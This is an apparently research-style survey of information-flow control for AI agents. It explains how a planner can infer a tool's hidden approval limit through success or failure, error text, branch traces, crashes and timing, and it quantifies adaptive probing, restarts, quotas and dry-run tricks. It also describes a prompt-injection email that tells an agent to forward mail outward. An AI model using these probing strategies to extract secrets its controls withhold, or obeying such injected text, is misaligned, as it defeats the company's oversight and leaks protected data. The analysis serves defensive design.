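# Implicit flows and probing channels when an AI planner tests its tools

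## How a planner learns from a tool whose output it cannot read

An AI agent is a language model that uses software tools on someone's behalf, such as to search a mailbox or pay an invoice. The planner is the model that decides which tools to call, in what order, and with what arguments. Tools handle both private data and data written by strangers, so several research groups have proposed governing agents with information-flow control, a method from the 1970s that labels data and allows each movement of data only if the labels permit it. Some of these designs hide tool results from the planner. But the planner still makes the calls, and it can often see whether a call worked, what error came back, or how long the answer took, and can learn about the hidden data from these observations.

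### The agent loop and prompt injection

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, describe how an AI agent usually works as a loop. Ordinary software sends the model the conversation so far and a list of available tools. The model replies with either text for the user or a request to call a tool. If the model requests a call, the software makes it, appends the result to the conversation and queries the model again, repeating until the model produces a final answer.

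An attacker can also reach the planner through the appended results. In a prompt injection, someone hides instructions in material that the agent will read as it works. Costa and colleagues give the example of a user who asks the agent to summarize recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. One of the emails tells the agent to send the top message in the mailbox to an outside address, and a planner that treats this as an instruction has all the access it needs to comply. Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, attribute the weakness to instructions and data reaching the model through the same channel of natural language. They also point out that an attack doesn't need instructions. If the plan is to pay whatever account the invoice names, an attacker can divert the payment by putting a false account number on the invoice.

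### Labels and hidden results

A label in these systems usually has two parts, one for secrecy and one for trust. For example, data from a corporate database is secret and trusted, while web search results are public and untrusted. Anything computed from several inputs takes the stricter label for each part, so a text that draws on both sources is secret and untrusted. A label can also be a list of the people allowed to read the data. If Ann, Bo and Cy may read one document, and Bo, Cy and Di another, only Bo and Cy may read a summary of the two. Sabelfeld and Myers (2003) explain in *Language-Based Information-Flow Security* that trust, or integrity, mirrors secrecy, since secrecy rules keep information from reaching the wrong destinations and integrity rules keep it from arriving from the wrong sources.

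As the system runs, taint tracking passes these labels from each input to everything computed from it. Before each tool call, the software checks the labels against a policy. For example, the policy might let the system send an email only if every recipient is allowed to read its contents and the request to send it came from trusted data.

This scheme is hard to apply to language models because nobody can say in general which parts of its input a model used for a given reply. A cautious system therefore gives each reply the combined label of everything in the conversation, but then a single untrusted email stops the planner from sending any more messages. To avoid this, the system can store the tool's result in a variable and show the planner only the variable's name. The planner can still request that the variable's contents be sent to a colleague, and the software fills them in. If the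 text needs interpreting, a quarantined model, which can read such data but cannot call tools, interprets it and stores its answer in another variable.

### Explicit and implicit flows

Suppose that a company gives its planner a purchasing tool. The tool accepts an order of x thousand dollars only if x is at most a hidden approval limit, which is one of the whole numbers from 1 to 1,024. The planner may use the tool but is not meant to learn the limit. (The company may fear that a planner that knows the limit will spend up to it, or mention it to a supplier.) The limit is secret, and since the company itself set it, it is also trusted. Now take three lines of code that run somewhere inside the tool:

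```
copy  := limit
large := false
if limit > 500 then large := true
```

The first line is an explicit flow because it copies the secret, and a taint tracker will mark `copy` as secret. The other two lines create an implicit flow. They write only the constants "false" and "true", which are not secret, but anyone who reads `large` afterward knows whether the limit is above 500.

The distinction is about fifty years old. *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow* (Denning and Denning, 1977) illustrated it with an even shorter program, which sets y to 1 and then resets it to 0 if x is 0. If x can only be 0 or 1, y always ends up equal to x. A year earlier, *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976) had pointed out that the information flows whether or not the conditional assignment runs. A reader who finds `large` still false learns that the limit is at most 500,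 even though the machine skipped the conditional assignment.

A system can catch implicit flows by labeling the current point of execution as well as the data, an idea Denning credits to J. S. Fenton. When the program enters a conditional, the system adds the label of the tested data to this program-counter label, and it restores the old label when the program leaves. Anything the program writes inside the conditional must be at least as secret as the program-counter label. In the third line above, that label is secret, so `large` becomes secret when the assignment runs. A monitor that labels only executed writes misses the flow when the assignment does not run, as Fenton already knew.

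The general reason for this difficulty, according to Sabelfeld and Myers, is that confidentiality depends on all the paths a program could take, but a run-time monitor observes only one. To be safe, the monitor could keep the program-counter label secret for the rest of the run. But then labels only ever rise, and results end up too secret for their intended use, an effect known as label creep. This would severely restrict an agent, because the conditional is often in the planner itself. When an order fails, the planner decides to try a smaller one, and every decision it makes from then on depends on the limit.

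### The five channels

Butler Lampson's three-page *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (1973), which came before Denning's work, considers a customer who runs someone else's service program on private data and wants to be sure that the program cannot pass the data to the program's owner. Denying the program access to files is not enough, and Lampson lists some of the ways it could still leak the data. It can leave a temporary file where its owner will look, encode data in the bill, or open and close a file in a pattern that another program detects by trying to open the same file. It can also alternate between heavy computing and heavy disk use, so that a program running alongside can detect the machine slowing down. Lampson called this last kind of path a covert channel, meaning one not intended for information transfer at all.

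Lampson's service deliberately tries to leak data by finding a way to encode it. The purchasing tool only applies its rule, but the planner can still learn about the limit from it through five channels.

The simplest channel is whether a call succeeds or fails. If an order for 500 goes through, the limit is at least 500, and if it is refused, the limit is lower. The planner can learn this even when the receipt is hidden in a variable. Denning describes a deliberate use of the same channel, in which a program that holds a secret number x commits exactly x security violations, and its owner later counts them in the record of aborted operations. To limit this leak, the system could keep no such record, or start one only after some number of violations, but Denning notes that this makes debugging harder. Agents have the same problem, since a planner that is never told about failed calls cannot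 correct them.

Error messages can reveal much more than a bare refusal. A message that quotes the limit reveals it immediately, but less explicit messages also provide information. If the tool checks the supplier before the amount, "unknown supplier" means the order failed the first check, and "not approved" means it reached the second. Attackers have long used such differences. In *Multi-run security*, Birgisson and Sabelfeld mention an exploit against ASP.NET, Microsoft's web framework, that compared the error messages from many requests to mount a padding oracle attack, which decrypts data by observing how a server reacts to altered ciphertext.

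The branch that a program takes may leave traces even if the planner sees neither the result nor an error. Suppose the planner writes a complete plan in advance to place an order and, if the tool refuses it, to file a request with the finance department. Nothing comes back to the planner. Later, on another task, it reads the finance department's queue, finds the request, and can infer that the tool refused the order. Denning and Denning describe a simpler version, in which a process transmits the number x by locking x files, which an observer then counts.

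Termination is the fourth channel. Suppose a cruder tool raises an error when an order exceeds the limit, and no other code handles the error, so the whole run stops. When the planner next starts, it finds its task unfinished and can infer why. In an example from Denning and Denning, a crash reveals nearly all of a secret number x. Their program repeatedly adds x to a running total and, after each addition, writes the number of additions so far to a public file. It never tests x, but it halts when the total grows too large for the machine's register. Dividing the largest number the register can hold by the last count in the file gives approximately x. Their certification method, as first designed, would have passed this program. They proposed disabling all such halts except those for which the programmer had declared a response, so that the method could check the response too.

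The remaining channel is timing. An order within the limit might take four seconds because it goes on to the supplier's computer, while one above the limit comes back immediately. A language model has no clock, so the surrounding software has to supply the time, for example through timestamps in the conversation or a tool that reports it. Noise in the response times then gives less protection than one might hope. Lampson observed that a suitable encoding gets information through reliably however small the effect on the system's performance, provided it is not zero, although the rate may be very low. That argument assumes a sender who cooperates, but without one the planner can repeat the measurement instead. Denning and Denning state that running time is beyond the reach of their method.

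### Noninterference and its exception for termination

A guarantee that covers all five channels has to be about what someone can see. Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, gave it the form that later work has kept. One group of users does not interfere with another if nothing the first group does affects what the second group sees. If the first group's commands are removed from any sequence of commands and the rest are run, each member of the second group must see the same output as before. Their example is a file that does not exist at the start. If the first group may not interfere with a certain user, the system must keep reporting to that user that the file does not exist, even after someone has created it.

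For a single program the condition fits on one line. Let out(L, x) stand for everything the observer sees when the secret is L and the public input is x. Noninterference requires

out(L₁, x) = out(L₂, x) for all secrets L₁ and L₂ and every input x.

The purchasing tool fails this because, with x = 500, it declines the order if the limit is 300 and accepts it if the limit is 700.

Most working systems aim for a weaker guarantee. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, prove what they describe as the standard kind, termination-insensitive noninterference, under which secrets may affect whether a run finishes but nothing else. For a program whose only output comes at the end, the equation above has to hold only when both runs finish. Without this exception, a designer would have to forbid every loop that depends on a secret or prove that each one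 ends. People have usually defended the exception by saying that whether a program finishes can reveal at most one bit per run.

The cruder purchasing tool either returns "accepted" or crashes. Any two runs that finish return the same word, so the tool satisfies the termination-insensitive condition, which compares only runs that finish. Yet the planner learns just as much from this tool as from the version that returns "declined" instead of crashing.

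An uncaught error or a memory overflow has the same effect as an infinite loop, according to Askarov, Hunt and colleagues in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit*. In the system of Garby and colleagues, a failed policy check also stops the run, so whether the policy blocked an attempt falls under the exception for termination as well. Askarov and colleagues also show that the defence that termination leaks only one bit fails once a program produces output as it runs. Their counterexample counts upwards, publishes each number, and hangs when it reaches the secret. A planner does much the same when it orders $1,000 worth of goods, then $2,000, then $3,000, until the run stops.

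### When the planner is the observer

Agent researchers adopted these techniques to protect the planner from prompt injection. Costa and colleagues trust the user's messages and the model. Their adversary is an outsider who tampers with the data that tools fetch. This outsider may notice certain effects of tool calls, such as a visit in a website's statistics, but never sees what passes between the software and the model. Girrens and Wang also allow the adversary to run some of the tools. They still place the planner on the defenders' side, and they set aside failures of the model's alignment that do not come from information flow.

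Keeping the approval limit from the planner is a different task, because the guarantee should now bound what the planner itself can learn. The labels and checks may be the same software as before, but different things count as visible. Sabelfeld and Myers insist that a system protects confidential information only relative to a model of what attackers can observe. For example, power consumption is of little interest to an attacker on most computers, but it becomes a serious leak on a smart card, which draws its power from a terminal that may be hostile. Similarly, an outsider may never see the outcome of a tool call, whereas the planner usually sees it first. Costa and colleagues prove explicit secrecy, which covers only explicit flows. That is defensible against an outsider who sees occasional side effects, but it doesn't limit what the planner can infer from a call's success or failure.

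The two purposes also depend on different halves of the label, trust for preventing injection and secrecy for preventing leaks. An injection defence is mainly meant to stop untrusted data from steering the planner. The reply "declined" depends on the order and on a limit the company set, so it can be trustworthy, and a check on trust alone would let it through. It is also too short to carry an instruction. A designer worried about injection can therefore reasonably allow it, but the reply still reveals information about the limit, which matters if the limit is secret.

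It also matters who picks the inputs. The termination-insensitive condition compares single runs, and Birgisson and Sabelfeld argue that this conceals an assumption that the program runs only once. They compare two tiny programs. One loops forever if the secret is anything but zero, so running it again gives an attacker the same answer. The other loops forever if the secret equals a number that the attacker supplies. Both are secure by the single-run standard, but the second lets the attacker try one number after another until it hangs. In an experiment, they took a program certified by Jif, a version of Java with built-in flow checking, and extracted about one secret bit per second from it on an ordinary desktop machine. The purchasing tool is like the second program, because the planner chooses x, sees the outcome and chooses the next x accordingly. This puts the planner in a far stronger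 position than someone who can only plant a sentence in an email and hope it works.

In *Reconciling progress-insensitive noninterference and declassification*, Bay and Askarov consider a weaker treatment of termination reasonable when one trusts the code not to exploit such leaks aggressively, but think that untrusted code calls for the stronger one. In an agent, the planner decides the sequence of calls, and in some designs it also writes the program that makes them. Trusting that code therefore means trusting the planner, which the guarantee is supposed to restrain.

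Lampson proposed that the customer should determine everything the service puts into its outgoing channels, including the amount of the bill. The service may still refuse the job, and Lampson compares the arrangement to an industrial purchase order. It works because the customer owns the secret and gains nothing by dictating a figure it already knows. If the secret belongs to the service, as the approval limit does, the service can leak it by refusing.

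The definitions are still useful for the new purpose. Garby and colleagues state theirs for an observer at any level of secrecy, so one can put the planner at the public level and count every outcome as visible. Birgisson and Sabelfeld point out that full noninterference, with termination included, holds over any number of runs, because if no run reveals anything, repeating it reveals nothing either. But a purchasing tool cannot satisfy it while giving the planner honest answers, because an honest answer to an order for 500 depends on the limit. A company that wants a working tool has to decide which limits the planner may tell apart. Birgisson and Sabelfeld write such a decision as a division of the possible secrets into classes, where the observer may learn the class but not the member. The company might accept that the planner finds out whether the limit is below 500. The tool as described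 does not enforce any such restriction. A planner free to try every order can identify any of the 1,024 limits, since the limit is the largest order that the tool accepts.

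## How much repeated probes reveal

Trying every order in turn could take the planner more than a thousand calls. It can find the limit much faster by choosing each order based on earlier replies, and a simple count shows how fast any such strategy can be.

### Counting the transcripts

Let k be the number of outcomes the planner can tell apart after one probe, and q the number of probes. An outcome includes everything the planner sees, so if a tool has two possible replies, and either can arrive after three recognizably different delays, k is 6. The transcript is the sequence of outcomes from all q probes. Each probe has at most k possible outcomes, whatever the earlier outcomes were, so there are at most k^q transcripts.

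This count also applies to a planner that adapts its probes to earlier answers. Its strategy is a rule that chooses the next probe from the transcript so far, so the transcript determines which probes it sent. If the planner makes some choices at random, the same count applies to each possible outcome of those choices. As long as the tool does not behave randomly, each possible secret leads to one transcript. The strategy therefore sorts the secrets into at most k^q groups, and the planner learns only which group contains the secret.

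One bit is the amount of information that halves a set of equally likely possibilities. If all 1,024 limits are equally likely, the planner starts out 10 bits short of knowing the limit, because 1,024 is 2^10. Sorting the limits into k^q groups supplies, on average, at most

log₂(k^q) = q · log₂(k) bits.

*Synthesis of Adaptive Side-Channel Attacks*, by Phan, Bang and colleagues, uses the same bound for attackers who adapt. The leak is at most the logarithm of the number of distinct observation sequences. This number also limits guessing, because the planner has one best guess per transcript, so its chance of naming the right limit is at most k^q / 1,024.

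The bound applies to the average leak, so a lucky guess can reveal more. If the planner asks whether the limit is exactly 700 and is right, it gains all 10 bits from a probe with only two outcomes. The bound also depends on the designer's count of outcomes. Free-form error text can vary in so many ways that q · log₂(k) soon exceeds the size of the secret, which makes the bound useless. For the bound to be useful, the designer has to restrict the tool to a short list of replies.

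### The question matters as much as the count

Suppose the purchasing tool's limit is 700. The planner first orders 513, and the tool accepts, so the limit lies between 513 and 1,024. The tool then refuses 769, accepts 641 and refuses 705, which narrows the range to 641 to 704. Six more orders, for 673, 689, 697, 701, 699 and 700, leave only one candidate. Each order halves the range, so 10 probes always suffice. No strategy can guarantee success with nine, because nine accept-or-refuse replies can form only 512 different sequences, too few to distinguish 1,024 possible limits.

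If the tool's error messages include the limit, one probe is enough. The planner orders 1,024. If the tool accepts, the limit is 1,024. Otherwise, the error message gives the limit. This probe has 1,024 possible outcomes and reveals all 10 bits.

At the other extreme is a tool that answers only "is it exactly x?". Password checkers work this way, and Bultan (2021), in *Quantitative Information Flow and Side Channels*, points out that even one with no other leak gives something away, because it must tell users whether their guess matched. On the first probe, "yes" is worth 10 bits but has a chance of 1 in 1,024. "No" rules out a single candidate, which is worth about 0.0014 bits. The average is

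(1/1,024) · 10 + (1,023/1,024) · 0.0014 ≈ 0.011 bits.

The planner's best strategy is to guess the candidates one by one without repeats, which takes about 512 probes on average. This tool has two outcomes, as does the one that accepts or refuses orders, so the same counting bound applies to both. But 10 exact guesses can sort the limits into only 11 groups, 10 of which contain a single limit, so they yield about 0.11 bits on average, compared with 10 bits from 10 well-chosen orders.

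A small side-channel leak can greatly reduce the number of guesses an attacker needs. Balasch, in *Introduction to Side-Channel Attacks*, gives the example of a four-digit PIN, which takes about 5,000 guesses on average if the checker reveals only whether each guess is right. But if the checker compares the digits one at a time and stops at the first wrong one, its running time shows how many leading digits are correct. An attacker can then find each digit separately, in about 20 guesses altogether.

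### Köpf and Basin's model of adaptive attacks

Köpf and Basin developed a general account of such probing in *An Information-Theoretic Model for Adaptive Side-Channel Attacks* (2007). A side channel reveals information through something other than a system's intended output, such as its running time or power use. They studied attacks on encryption hardware, but their model fits tool calls with little change.

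A system holds a fixed key and responds to messages. The attacker picks a message m and observes f(key, m), where f is a known function. Two keys are indistinguishable under m if they produce the same observation. Each message therefore divides the possible keys into non-overlapping blocks, and the observation reveals which block contains the system's key. For the purchasing tool, an order of 513 divides the possible limits into 1–512 and 513–1,024. A strategy is a tree with the full set of keys at the root. At each node, the attacker chooses a message that splits the remaining keys further.

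Suppose there are four possible keys, 1 to 4, and an attacker can send three messages. Message A separates {1} from {2, 3, 4}, B separates {1, 2} from {3, 4}, and C separates {1, 2, 3} from {4}. The attacker sends B first, then A if the key is 1 or 2, or C if it is 3 or 4. This identifies any key in two steps, whereas an attacker who had to choose all the messages in advance would need all three.

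The gap between fixed and adaptive probing widens quickly as the number of possibilities grows. For the purchasing tool, only an order of 700 can distinguish a limit of 699 from a limit of 700, and every other neighboring pair likewise requires its own order. A planner that must fix its list of orders in advance therefore needs 1,023 of them to be sure of the limit, while one that can choose each order after seeing the previous reply needs 10. This is a reason to make a planner write its whole plan before it sees any outcome. But the plan could contain the halving procedure as code, and the planner would then need to see only where the procedure ended to learn the limit.

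Köpf and Basin measure a system's resistance by the average uncertainty that remains after n steps of the best possible attack. For the purchasing tool, this is 10 − n bits. They also use guessing entropy, the average number of "is it exactly x?" questions the attacker would still need to ask. After five well-chosen orders, 32 possible limits remain and the guessing entropy is 16.5. Guessing entropy is useful if the planner can later check its guesses somewhere else.

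Finding the best attack by exhaustive search is impractical because the number of possible trees grows too quickly. Köpf and Basin instead use a greedy rule, which always picks the message that leaves the least uncertainty after the next step. For the purchasing tool, this rule halves the remaining possibilities at each step. They tested the rule on simulated arithmetic circuits with keys of two to eight bits. In a circuit that multiplies integers, the running time depends only on how many 1s the key contains, so further messages reveal nothing new. On a more complicated circuit, one timing measurement revealed more than the number of 1s, and a second could reveal the rest of the key.

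In the model, the attacker knows the system fully and has unlimited computing power. A planner usually has only a tool's description and may need some probes just to learn how the tool behaves, so the model's figures are best read as the worst case.

### What a single run can leak by stopping

Halving works because the planner can probe again after a refusal. The cruder purchasing tool described earlier crashes instead of refusing, which ends the run. This tool satisfies termination-insensitive noninterference, and Askarov and colleagues analyzed how much protection that guarantee gives when a program produces output as it runs.

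The guarantee limits changes in the observer's knowledge, meaning the set of secrets consistent with everything seen so far. The observer may learn something from the existence of each new output, but must learn nothing more from its value. For a given public input, every secret therefore produces the same sequence of outputs, and a secret can change only where the sequence stops. An observer who waits for t outputs can distinguish only t + 1 cases, because the program either stops after some number of outputs from 0 to t − 1 or reaches t. Two possible outcomes at each step would ordinarily allow 2^t transcripts, but here one of the two ends the run.

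Two theorems follow for a secret of N bits. First, no program that satisfies the guarantee can reliably reveal the secret in time polynomial in N. To separate all 2^N secrets, the observer needs at least t = 2^N − 1 outputs, which amounts to a brute-force search. Second, if all secrets are equally likely, t outputs raise the observer's chance of guessing correctly from 1/2^N to at most (t + 1)/2^N, an advantage of at most t/2^N.

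To find a 10-bit limit by brute force, the planner starts at 2 and goes up by one until the tool crashes, which takes 1,023 orders, or 17 minutes at one second per call. Askarov and colleagues leaked a 32-bit number in under six seconds on a 3 GHz machine, using a program that passes standard flow checking. From this they estimated that a credit card number of about 50 bits would take about 18½ days, and judged 128-bit encryption keys out of reach. Calls to an agent's tools are far slower than steps of a compiled program, and at one call per second a 32-bit secret would take about 136 years to find. The theorems therefore offer real protection for long random secrets, but very little for an approval limit, a diagnosis or the answer to a yes-or-no question.

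They also assume that the program is deterministic, that the observer knows the program and can recognize when it has stopped producing output, and that there is only one run, with a public input that does not change. (For programs with random behavior, Garby and colleagues bound the leak by the average probability that a run does not finish.) The second theorem also assumes that all secrets are equally likely, but real approval limits tend to be round numbers, so a planner could try 50, 100, 250 and 500 and skip most of the values in between.

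### Restarting the run

If the planner can restart after a crash and choose a new order, a crash is like any other reply. With unlimited restarts, there are again 2^q possible transcripts, and the planner can find the limit in 10 orders by halving the remaining range each time.

Even a few restarts help a great deal. With q orders and at most c crashes, the number of transcripts is the number of ways to place up to c crashes among q positions:

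1 + q + q(q − 1)/2 + …, with one term for each number of crashes from 0 to c.

With one restart, and so at most two crashes, the planner needs the first three terms to add up to at least 1,024, which happens at q = 45. It orders 46, then 90, then 133, with each increase one smaller than the last. When the tool crashes, the planner restarts it and increases the order by one at a time from the last accepted value.

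| Restarts allowed | Orders needed in the worst case |
|---|---|
| 0 | 1,023 |
| 1 | 45 |
| 2 | 19 |
| 3 | 13 |
| 4 | 11 |
| 9 | 10 |

Birgisson and Sabelfeld show the same effect with a program that hangs if the secret and the attacker's input both have a 1 in the same position. The attacker sets one position of the input at a time and so learns the secret bit by bit. They measured a rate of one bit per second, which is fast enough to reveal a credit card number within a minute, compared with an estimated 18½ days for a single run.

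A planner cannot continue a search across runs if it starts each one with an empty conversation and no access to earlier results. A retry loop often carries that history from one run to the next, and Garby and colleagues identify such a loop around CaMeL, an agent design in which the planner writes its plan as code.

Birgisson and Sabelfeld's remedy is to forbid secret data and attacker-chosen data from jointly determining whether a program finishes. Their checker would reject a tool that crashes when the order exceeds the limit. But the purchasing tool has to compare the order with the limit to do its job. The company could have the tool return an ordinary refusal instead of crashing, but then the planner could use the accept-or-refuse replies to halve the range of possible limits with each order. If the company wants the planner to learn only whether the limit is below 500, the tool has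 to base its answer to every order on that fact alone.

### What slows probing

A quota on calls is the most direct obstacle because it caps q. After three orders, at least 128 limits remain possible on average, if all were equally likely at the start. A quota is very effective against exact guesses. Balasch notes that if a card allows three tries at a four-digit PIN, a thief has 3 chances in 10,000 of guessing it.

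How well a quota protects the limit depends on what it counts. If the company locks the planner out after its third refusal but does not count accepted orders, the arithmetic is the same as for three crashes, and 19 orders are enough to find the limit. The PIN routine on Balasch's slides has a similar weakness because it resets its counter after every correct entry. A thief who can make two guesses between the owner's uses will never reach the third failure. A quota of three orders a day lets the planner find the limit on the fourth day, or sooner if several agents share their results. No quota protects a yes-or-no secret that a single permitted call can reveal, or any secret that an error message quotes in full.

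If noise makes one reply in ten wrong, independently of the others, the planner can ask each question five times and take the majority answer, which is wrong less than 1% of the time. Asking ten questions this way takes fifty orders and finds the limit with a probability above 90%. Repetition fails to remove the noise only if the tool gives the same wrong answer each time. Bang, Rosner and Bultan (2018) automated a more sophisticated version in *Online Synthesis of Adaptive Side-Channel Attacks Based On Noisy Observations*. Their method first profiles the program to build a model of the noise, then uses that model to choose each new input during the attack.

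Some noise occurs without the designer adding it. A run can hang because of a bug or an unresponsive server, as *Nonmalleable Progress Leakage* (2025) notes, so a planner cannot be sure that a stopped run means the order was too large. Adding noise deliberately is more practical for delays than for decisions, because a purchasing tool that refuses one valid order in ten does its job badly. The designer can also pad delays so that every response takes the same time, which reduces the number of outcomes instead of adding noise.

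Accepted calls often have real consequences. In the example with a limit of 700, the tool accepts seven of the ten orders, and the company buys $4.6 million worth of goods, which someone is likely to notice. But the planner can make fewer purchases, with more refusals, by starting at the top. If it orders 1,024, then 1,023, and so on down, the first order the tool accepts equals the limit, so the planner learns it exactly with one purchase of $700,000 after 324 refusals. If it is willing to make two purchases, 45 calls are enough. These long runs of refusals are conspicuous to anyone who reads the logs. Phan and colleagues suggest using the attack trees their software generates as signatures for filtering out real attacks.

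Probing has no consequences if the tool has a dry-run or validation mode, which reports whether an order would go through without placing it. Designers add such modes so that an agent can check its work before doing something irreversible, but the agent can also use them to probe. Free cancellation has much the same effect. A planner may even be able to improvise a dry run by ordering from a supplier that does not exist, if the tool checks the amount before the supplier. The tool then answers "not approved" if the amount is over the limit and "unknown supplier" if it is within the limit, and places no order in either case.

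These calculations assume that the secret stays the same. If the company draws a new limit at random every day and allows three orders a day, the planner learns at most three bits, on average, about any one limit, and the previous day's answers don't help. This protection fails if the planner can make ten calls before the next change, or if the new value depends on the old one. For example, if the limit is what remains of a monthly budget, each accepted order lowers it by an amount the planner knows, so the planner can subtract that amount and keep probing. The company also can't protect fixed facts this way, such as a customer's diagnosis or an employee's past salary.

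## What tools tell models after a failed call, and what models learn from it

A planner can find the approval limit in 10 orders even if the purchasing tool answers only "accepted" or "declined". Most real tools explain their refusals, because a model that knows why a call failed can often correct the call. If the explanation states the limit, the planner doesn't need to search for it.

### How the Model Context Protocol reports errors

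The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a common standard for connecting AI applications to tools. A server offers the tools, and a client inside the application sends it the model's calls and returns the results. The server and client, often written by different developers, therefore both affect what the planner sees after a failure.

The current specification, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (July 28, 2026), gives a server two ways to report a failure. A protocol error replaces the result and means that the request itself was faulty, such as one naming a tool that does not exist, or that the server broke down. A tool execution error looks like an ordinary result, except that its `isError` field is set to `true` and its text explains the problem. Servers use it when an outside service fails, when an input is invalid (such as a date in the wrong format or a value out of range), or when a call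 breaks a business rule (such as an order above the approval limit).

Under the MCP specification, clients "should" show tool execution errors to the model so it can correct itself, and they "may" show it protocol errors too. A client that follows this advice gives the planner the full text of the purchasing tool's refusal. Returning the refusal as a protocol error would not reliably hide it, because the specification lets the client decide whether to show such errors, although the guide to MCP's TypeScript library, Model Context Protocol's *Errors*, describes them as ones the model never sees. Even a client that withholds the message has to give the model something in its place or end the run, and the planner can learn from either.

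Until late 2025, the Model Context Protocol's rules were ambiguous about bad inputs. They classed "invalid arguments" as protocol errors and "invalid input data" as tool execution errors. *Input Validation Errors as Tool Execution Errors* (2025), by the contributor fredericbarthelet, proposed sending all of these errors to the model. Its example is a flight-booking tool that accepts only future dates. The tool's machine-readable description can specify a date's format but cannot express a comparison with today. A model that sends a past date and never sees why it was rejected tends to repeat the mistake, and the proposal mentions that Cursor, a coding tool, would repeat the rejected call three times. If the error message says that dates must be in the future and gives today's date, the model can correct the call immediately. The proposal offers this only as an illustration and reports no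 measurements. The protocol's November 25, 2025 revision adopted the proposal (Model Context Protocol changelog, 2025).

Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) lists no change to this division in the July 2026 revision, but it does list the removal of sessions. This matters for probing because a server that counts one planner's calls now has to identify the planner some other way, for example by its credentials. The specification still requires servers to limit the rate of calls. It also requires them to "sanitize" their outputs, but doesn't explain what that means for an error message.

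### When the repair gives away the rule

The error message that helps a model fix its flight booking also discloses a rule missing from the tool's description. Disclosing that flights must leave in the future is harmless. But if the purchasing tool followed the same good practice, it would return "orders must not exceed $700,000". The planner could then correct its order in one step, but it would also learn the limit.

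The sample code in the TypeScript guide has the same problem. It defines a tool that reads a note by name. If the model asks for a note called "drafts", which does not exist, the error lists the names of all existing notes. The only one is "welcome", and the model can try again with that. The guide recommends such hints because the model has nothing else to work with. If a company had a note called "March layoffs", a single mistyped name would reveal that the note exists.

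This library also discloses error details by default. When a tool's code raises an exception, the library catches it and sends the exception's message to the model as text. A developer who writes no error messages may therefore still send the model whatever a database or another component put into its exception. The library also exempts errors from its check on the format of results. A designer might have used that check to limit a tool to a short list of replies, which is what makes the counting bound useful, but the check does not cover refusals.

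The specification does consider guessing in its advice on handles, the identifiers that a server issues for things like shopping baskets. It recommends handles with no visible structure, and long random ones where the server does not check who is calling. It also recommends that servers respond to an unknown or expired handle with an error that identifies the problem. A planner can use these errors to test whether a handle exists, but it is very unlikely to guess a long random handle because, as with encryption keys, there are too many possible values to try.

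Other software between the tool and the model could shorten or replace the error text. Woo, Conde and Reviriego (*Same Error, Different Recovery*, 2026) looked for this in October 2026 and found no inference engine (the software that runs a model) or gateway that rewrites failed tool results. Agent frameworks do more. OpenAI's Agents SDK turns an exception into a message through a function that the developer can change, so that function would be a convenient place to substitute a fixed phrase. Google's framework has a plugin that retries a failed tool up to three times and gives the model guidance on what to try. This helps with repairs but also gives the planner up to three more probes.

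### How much error text an agent needs

Whether a designer can reasonably cut the explanation depends on how much agents rely on it. Xu and Wu (2026), in *MCP Error Messages Written for Developers Hurt the Most Capable Agents Most*, first collected 3,001 error messages from the source code of 150 popular MCP servers. Nearly all gave the cause of the failure, and 949 also suggested a next step. They then took tasks from an established benchmark of tool use, made one call in each task fail, and varied the text returned. Five OpenAI models, from GPT-5.5 to GPT-6 Astra, continued from the same point. The agents could only call the benchmark's tools.

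| Reason for the failure | "Operation failed." | Cause stated | Cause and a correct next step |
|---|---|---|---|
| Wrong unit or format | 83% | 79% | 82% |
| Missing required field | 86% | 88% | 88% |
| Wrong tool | 80% | 81% | 81% |
| Nonexistent item | 98% | 98% | 97% |
| Expired login | 61% | 82% | 84% |
| Missing permission | 0% | 0% | 53% |
| Rate limit reached | 59% | 5% | 88% |

The figures are the share of tasks the agents completed after the failure, averaged over the five models. In the first four rows, the text of the error message made little difference because the mistake was visible in the agent's own call. For the nonexistent item, for instance, the failed call contained an identifier such as -999999, while the task named the right one. A designer could cut these messages to two words with almost no drop in task completion.

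In the last three rows, the call failed for a reason the agent could not see, and the explanation made a large difference. An approval limit is similar, since a well-formed order can exceed it. So explanations help agents most in the cases where they are most likely to disclose something hidden.

But the most useful text did not describe the hidden state in any detail. In those three rows the next step named a tool to call, as in "Call ticket_login first." The purchasing tool could similarly answer "not approved, use request_approval", and the planner could finish its task without seeing the number. It would still learn that the order was too large, so it could still find the limit by halving. The wording only avoids giving away more than the decision does. (Xu and Wu did not test a hidden threshold, so how well agents would recover with such a message is a guess.)

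In the rate-limit row, agents did much better with "Operation failed." than with the true cause, because many of them called again and the experiment enforced no waiting time. When they read that they had reached a limit, most gave up. Most also gave up after reading "Wait before retrying.", which GitHub's server uses, making an average of only 0.37 further tool calls per trial. GPT-6 Astra, the newest large model, took such text most literally. Its recovery rate after an expired login fell from 75% to 6% when the message included an instruction to run a terminal command, which the agents could not do.

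A tool, or a security layer in front of it, might therefore word its refusals to discourage probing. This could well reduce the number of probes an ordinary planner makes incidentally, but it guarantees nothing about a planner that is trying to find the limit, because that planner has a reason to ignore the advice.

Studies that remove or enrich error text in other settings give mixed results. *Masking Stale Observations Helps Search Agents -- Until It Doesn't* (2026) examines search agents that drop old tool results to save space. When the agents also dropped old error messages, their error rate in opening pages rose from 18.6% to 22.6% for a small model and from 20.4% to 24.6% for a somewhat larger one. Woo and colleagues cite an experiment in which feedback that listed the permitted alternatives raised one model's repairs from 14 to 36 out of 50 tasks, though such a list discloses about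 as much as an error message can. They cite another study in which agents writing database queries did about as well with raw database errors as with feedback tailored to the database's structure, because what mattered was noticing the failure and trying again.

Some of the benefit may also be available without further disclosure. Woo and colleagues' own method leaves the failed call in the conversation, repeats its error in a new message, and adds one stock sentence of guidance, for example that the failure is temporary and a retry should work. On the ToolMaze benchmark, this raised success after explicit errors by 14.2 points for open models with 7 to 8 billion parameters, and by 10.5 points for models with 32 to 70 billion. On a second benchmark, of 24 longer tasks, it made no measurable difference.

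### Learning hidden rules from chosen queries

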